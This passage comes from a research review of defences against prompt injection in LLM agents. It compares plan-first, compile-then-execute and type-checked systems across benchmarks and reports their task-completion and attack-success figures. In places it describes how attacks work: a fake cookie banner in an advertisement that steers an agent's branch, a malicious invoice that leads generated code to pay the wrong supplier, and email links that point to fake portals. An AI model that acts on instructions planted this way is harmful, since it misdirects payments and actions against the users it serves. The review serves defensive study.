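Li, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *AgentDyn*, found that only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 user tasks require dynamic planning, meaning that the agent learns some of the necessary steps only while carrying out the task. They wrote 60 new tasks that all require it, covering shopping, GitHub and daily life. These take 7.1 steps on average, compared with 3.5 in AgentDojo. In each one, the agent has to follow at least one helpful instruction from a third party, such as a request to log in before checkout.

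They tested four defences that restrict an agent according to the user's request. Tool Filter selects the tools the task seems to need and hides the rest. CaMeL sets the whole program in advance. Progent keeps rules about tool use and updates them as the agent works, and DRIFT starts from a plan but can approve departures from it. The table shows the share of tasks completed when there was no attack.

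| Defence | GPT-4o | Gemini 2.5 Pro | Claude Sonnet 3.5 | Llama 3.3 70B |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 53.3% | 51.7% | 60.0% | 10.0% |
| Tool Filter | 8.3% | 1.7% | 1.7% | 5.0% |
| CaMeL | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Progent | 6.7% | 25.0% | 13.3% | 3.3% |
| DRIFT | 30.0% | 36.7% | 33.3% | 11.7% |

Tool Filter often hid tools that looked irrelevant at the start but turned out to be essential. CaMeL's programs had no steps for instructions that appeared later. Progent could not reliably set accurate rules for so many tools, and its errors built up until it blocked almost everything useful. Attacks succeeded at most 5.9% of the time with these defences, compared with 12% to 38% without any. CaMeL's rate of zero means little, however, because it completed no tasks.

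For comparison, Li and colleagues tested Meta SecAlign, a version of Llama trained to ignore injected instructions. It works without a fixed plan. It completed 55% of the tasks, but about 9% of attacks against it succeeded.

The researchers also instructed agents not to ask the user for confirmation, because agents had often stopped to do so when something unexpected came up. An agent that asked the user about the portal notice would have failed the task, even though asking would have been the right thing to do.

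The two studies differ partly because their tasks were created differently. Every AgentDyn task needs new steps by design, so its results measure how badly fixed plans do on such tasks, not how common the tasks are. Benchmarks such as WebArena need outcomes that a program can check, which probably favours requests that spell out what the agent should do.

The studies also differ in what the proposer is assumed to know. Piet and colleagues assume complete documentation, so a program would log in before checkout because the documentation says to. An AgentDyn agent learns from the page that it must log in. The same task can therefore need new steps during execution in AgentDyn but not in the other study. Likewise, if the company's supplier table records who uses a portal, the invoice plan can include a branch for it. Neither study measures how often real users make requests that no one could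 plan in advance.

*AI Planning Framework for LLM-Based Web Agents* (Shahnovsky and Dror, 2026) reports 36.3% success on WebArena for an agent that wrote a full plan first and 38.4% for one that chose each step as it went. This comparison does not show which approach works better, because the planning agent saw every page and treated its plan only as guidance. The reported success rates for individual websites are also all below 13%, which is impossible to reconcile with those totals.

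### Baya

Baya, which Chow, Zhu and colleagues (2026) describe in *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm*, puts the idea of Piet and colleagues into practice. The two papers come from the same group at Berkeley. Baya handles a request in three steps:

1. A coding agent searches a catalogue of the website's functions and writes a Python program. It has no access to the website or the internet.
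2. The coding agent tests the program against simulated responses, including errors, and corrects it.
3. A separate process runs the program on the real website. If the program fails, the coding agent can write a new one, up to three times.

The researchers compared Baya with two ReAct agents on 581 WebArena tasks. One agent could use a browser and the same website functions as Baya, and the other could use only a browser.

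| Model | Baya | ReAct with website functions | ReAct with browser only |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 81.9% | 59.0% | 52.3% |
| Gemini 3.5 Flash | 78.5% | 70.7% | 50.9% |
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 72.8% | 70.4% | 62.0% |
| Average | 77.8% | 66.7% | 55.1% |

With Gemini and GPT-5.6 Luna, Baya's lead comes entirely from Postmill, where it solved 83% to 87% of tasks and the ReAct agents solved less than half. On the other 475 tasks, Baya solved 364 with Gemini and 335 with GPT-5.6 Luna, while the ReAct agent with website functions solved 366 and 363. With Claude, Baya was well ahead everywhere. A fixed program can therefore match an agent that adapts as it goes, at least on tasks like these, but the evidence that it does better is mixed.

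Some tasks are easier to do in a browser than with a program. To reorder an item in a browser, an agent finds the order and clicks "Reorder". A program has to look up the customer, find the order, create a cart, add the item, fill in the addresses and submit the order.

Baya also allows an unusually direct comparison of two plan languages, because an earlier version wrote its plans in JSON, with loops, conditions and filters but no general code, much like SPA's plans. That version completed about 59% of the same tasks on average, compared with 77.8% for the Python version. The gap was largest on the two shopping sites, where plans often have to go through many pages of results and build complicated requests. But the Python version used almost seven times as many tokens, so some of the gain may come from more thorough searching and testing.

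Piet and colleagues had expected model calls during execution in about 16% of the tasks on these four websites, but only 13 of 627 Baya programs (2.1%) contained one. Another 105 used a simple text-matching function that tolerates small differences in wording.

Chow and colleagues tested security with WASP, a benchmark that plants malicious instructions in web pages. None of its 84 attacks affected Baya's actions with any of three models. The ReAct agents had reported attack success rates of 16.2% with website functions and 25.5% without, counting every run in which the agent took a step towards the attacker's goal. Attackers achieved the goal itself only with one model on one website, in 5.6% of cases.

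These results concern attacks that add or redirect actions. Baya is not designed to stop an attacker from supplying false data, such as a false account number.

This protection makes tasks slower and more expensive. Baya averaged 327 seconds and $0.70 per task, compared with 87 seconds and $0.34 for ReAct with website functions. Reusing programs for repeated tasks would lower Baya's averages.

These costs do not include building the interfaces. The researchers inspected each website by hand, documented its functions and wrote browser scripts for whatever the functions did not cover. GitLab alone has 1,028 functions. The official documentation leaves out important rules. On the shopping site, for example, it lists size and colour as optional, but adding clothes to the cart fails without them.

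Someone also has to keep the interfaces up to date as the websites change. A model could do some of this work, but a malicious comment on a page might then influence the interface code, which every later program would trust.

Baya could pay through the supplier's portal only if someone had already built an interface to it. Writing a new program can correct a faulty call to an existing function but can't supply a function that is missing.

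### Foreseeing what will be on the screen

Computer-use agents look at screenshots, click and type. They have no list of website functions to plan with, and the effect of a click depends on what is on the screen. In NOVA, a method by Foerster and colleagues, the proposer still writes one complete plan before seeing the screen.

The plan repeats three steps. A quarantined model describes the current screen, a second call checks the description against a prediction such as "a cookie banner is visible", and the yes-or-no answer selects a branch. The proposer never receives the screen contents or the answer.

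The plans are long because they have to cover many possibilities, and about half of each plan never runs. On average they have 213 lines, 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines, 5 calls and 4 branches for CaMeL's plans on AgentDojo.

Foerster and colleagues tested NOVA on OSWorld, a benchmark of everyday computer tasks. The table covers only tasks that each model had already solved by working step by step. In the NOVA runs, the model being tested handled the screen and a separate model wrote the plans.

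| Model that handled the screen | Tasks it had solved step by step | Solved with one plan | Solved by at least one of five plans |
|---|---|---|---|
| UI-TARS 1.5 7B | 60 | 25 (41.7%) | 39 (65.0%) |
| OpenCUA 32B | 76 | 22 (28.9%) | 48 (63.2%) |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 109 | 31 (28.4%) | 62 (56.9%) |

The paper's headline claim, that NOVA retains up to 57% of a frontier model's performance, refers to the best of five plans. With a single plan, NOVA retained 28%. An agent that can't tell in advance which of the five plans will work would have to try them one after another, which is a bad idea if the plans send money.

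Branches help. With UI-TARS, plans written without them solved only 4 of the 60 tasks at the first attempt. The proposer's skill mattered more than the choice of screen-reading model.

Choosing steps during execution did not help much when the proposer could not see the screen. A variant based on FIDES, in which the proposer wrote one instruction at a time, solved 33.3% of the 60 tasks on the first attempt and 66.7% within five attempts. Compared with an unprotected agent, the variant used almost 30 times as many tokens, and NOVA used about twice as many.

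Every extra branch also gives an attacker another path to steer the agent into. Foerster and colleagues put a fake cookie banner inside an advertisement. The plan contained a branch for closing cookie banners, so the agent clicked on it and landed on the attacker's website. They call this branch steering. Checking the page's underlying code stopped the attack for simple advertisements but not for more elaborate ones, and a second model could not reliably tell fake banners from real ones.

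The invoice plan has the same weakness if one of its branches logs in at whatever address the email gives. Any sender could then direct the agent to a fake portal. The branch should take the address from the company's supplier table instead.

*ActGuard* (2026) has the agent predict, each time it chooses an action, which tools it might use in the next step only. The agent makes this prediction before it sees the result of the current action, so an instruction hidden in that result can't affect the prediction. If the agent then calls a tool it didn't predict, the system takes this into account when it audits the call but doesn't automatically block it. This lets the agent add unplanned steps. But a hidden instruction that stays in the agent's context could influence later predictions.

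### LACUNA: checking code as it is written

Another approach lets the agent write new steps during execution and checks each one before it runs. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) does this in Scala. A program can contain a gap, written `agent[T](task)`, where `task` is a request in English and `T` is the type of the result. When execution reaches the gap, a language model writes code to fill it. The compiler checks that code as if a programmer had written it there, and the code runs only if it passes.

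An invoice program might leave a gap for portal payments:

```scala
val paid = unpaidInvoices().map { inv =>
  findApproved(inv.supplierName) match
    case Some(s) if inv.amount < 50000 =>
      if inv.portalOnly then
        agent[Int](s"Pay through the portal: ${inv.text}")
      else pay(s, inv.amount)
    case _ => 0
}
```

For an invoice that requires the portal, the model might write:

```scala
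val session = portalLogin(s)
session.pay(inv.number, inv.amount)
```

The new code can use any variable or function available at that point in the program. If `portalLogin` accepts only an approved supplier and takes the address from the company's records, the code can't use it to log in through a link in the email. Code that calls a nonexistent function does not compile. LACUNA can also use TACIT's capability tracking to limit the effects of new code.

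The compiler accepts or rejects each piece of code as a whole. In an example from Zhao and colleagues, the model writes code that subtracts 50 from a balance and then returns text where the program requires a number. The compiler rejects the code, so the balance stays the same. Ordinary Python might have changed the balance before reaching the error.

The type check limits what new code can do, but code that passes it can still do the wrong thing. The gap above also has access to `pay`, and the prompt contains the text of the invoice. A malicious invoice could therefore lead the model to write code that pays a different approved supplier. The developer can prevent this by making fewer functions available in the gap.

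A checker also never has the complete plan. Before execution, it can list the functions available in the gap, but it can't determine which of them the new code will call, how often, or in what order. A person who wanted to approve the whole plan would have to review each piece as it appeared, perhaps after the agent had already paid several invoices.

New code can itself contain gaps, so one call to the model can lead to others. This makes LACUNA very flexible. For example, a ReAct loop is code that calls a few tools and ends with another gap for the same task. But the calls may never stop, and neither the compiler nor the runtime can distinguish a hard task from an endless one. LACUNA therefore lets developers limit how deeply the calls are nested.

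A depth limit does not keep the total small. If each piece of code contains $b$ gaps and the limit allows $d$ levels below the first call, the number of calls can reach

$$1 + b + b^2 + \dots + b^d.$$

Ten gaps and five levels result in 111,111 calls. A loop around a gap can add more, so an agent also needs a limit on total time or spending.

Zhao and colleagues first tested LACUNA on BrowseComp-Plus, a set of difficult research questions. With DeepSeek V4 Flash, LACUNA answered 27.1% of them correctly. The compiler rejected 8.6% of the code, and each question needed 0.7 retries on average. They conclude that the checks did not reduce accuracy, but they did not run the same agent without them.

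The customer service benchmark τ²-bench provides a better comparison, because a standard agent that called tools directly attempted the same 392 tasks.

| Tasks | DeepSeek V4 Flash, tool calls | DeepSeek V4 Flash, LACUNA | Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, tool calls | Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, LACUNA |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Retail | 80.9% | 58.8% | 52.6% | 43.9% |
| Airline | 75.5% | 70.0% | 56.0% | 38.0% |
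| Telecom | 100.0% | 88.6% | 15.8% | 14.9% |
| Telecom workflow | 95.4% | 83.3% | 21.1% | 24.6% |
| Overall | 90.0% | 76.0% | 33.2% | 29.1% |

LACUNA's 76.0% is 14 percentage points below the standard agent's score, though the paper describes them as on par. Part of the problem is that the models had difficulty writing the code. The compiler rejected 22.4% of DeepSeek's code on the retail tasks, which led to 7.1 retries per task. Gemini's rejection rate ranged from 3.2% on retail to 89% on telecom. The comparison doesn't separate the effect of the type checks from that of writing Scala instead of calling tools directly.

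On AgentDojo, 8 of 1,898 attacks succeeded against LACUNA across two models, compared with 1 against TACIT. LACUNA completed 2 to 7 percentage points more of the users' tasks than TACIT in seven of the eight combinations of model and environment. An attack can still succeed if it gets the model to misuse a permission that the task requires.

### What the proposer learns after a failure

SPA, Baya and LACUNA differ in how much they tell the proposer when something goes wrong.

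| System | Failure | What the proposer receives | Further attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| SPA | The checker rejects the plan, or a step fails during execution | Nothing | None |
| Baya | The program fails on the live website | The old program and a restricted error message | Up to three |
| LACUNA | The compiler rejects new code | The compiler's error messages | Up to a limit that the developer sets |

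Girrens and Wang withhold all feedback from the proposer so that an attacker's text can't reach it that way. This makes sense for failures during execution. If a tool rejects an invoice and quotes part of it in the error message, a proposer that received the message would read text written by the invoice's sender.

It is less clear that SPA needs to withhold the checker's objections. The check runs before any tool does and uses the plan, the policy and the labels, not the contents of an email, so its objections could not pass on text from the inbox. *Soteria* does return its checker's objections, and LACUNA's compiler errors also come before the rejected code has run. But in LACUNA, text from an email can still reach the model through the request itself, as in the invoice example.

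Baya's error messages come from a live website, so they need more care. The interface may report that a required quantity is missing, but the protection fails if the message includes a review, a username or anything else that a user of the site wrote.

An attacker might still influence which error occurs, for example by submitting a badly formed invoice. If the interface has 32 possible messages, each failure conveys at most five bits, and three failures convey at most 15. Those bits could affect how the proposer rewrites the program, but they are too few to spell out an instruction.

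If Baya fails partway through, the new program must also avoid repeating payments the old one made. LACUNA avoids this problem for code the compiler rejects, because none of that code has run. But it doesn't retry code that compiles and then does the wrong thing.

Baya might miss the notice on the portal, because it writes a new program only after a failure. A bank transfer may go through without an error even if the supplier no longer wants bank transfers. The program has to check for such notices, so the proposer must have anticipated them.

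Chow and colleagues suggest returning control to the user when the program can't handle a requirement. The agent could pay the other invoices and report that one supplier asks for payment through a portal. If the user recognises the change as genuine, they can make a new request, and Baya can write a program for it. This takes longer, but the new instruction comes from the user rather than the email.

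Piet and colleagues also suggest that an agent could, if the user agrees, switch to working step by step with reduced permissions, such as read-only access or separate approval for every change.
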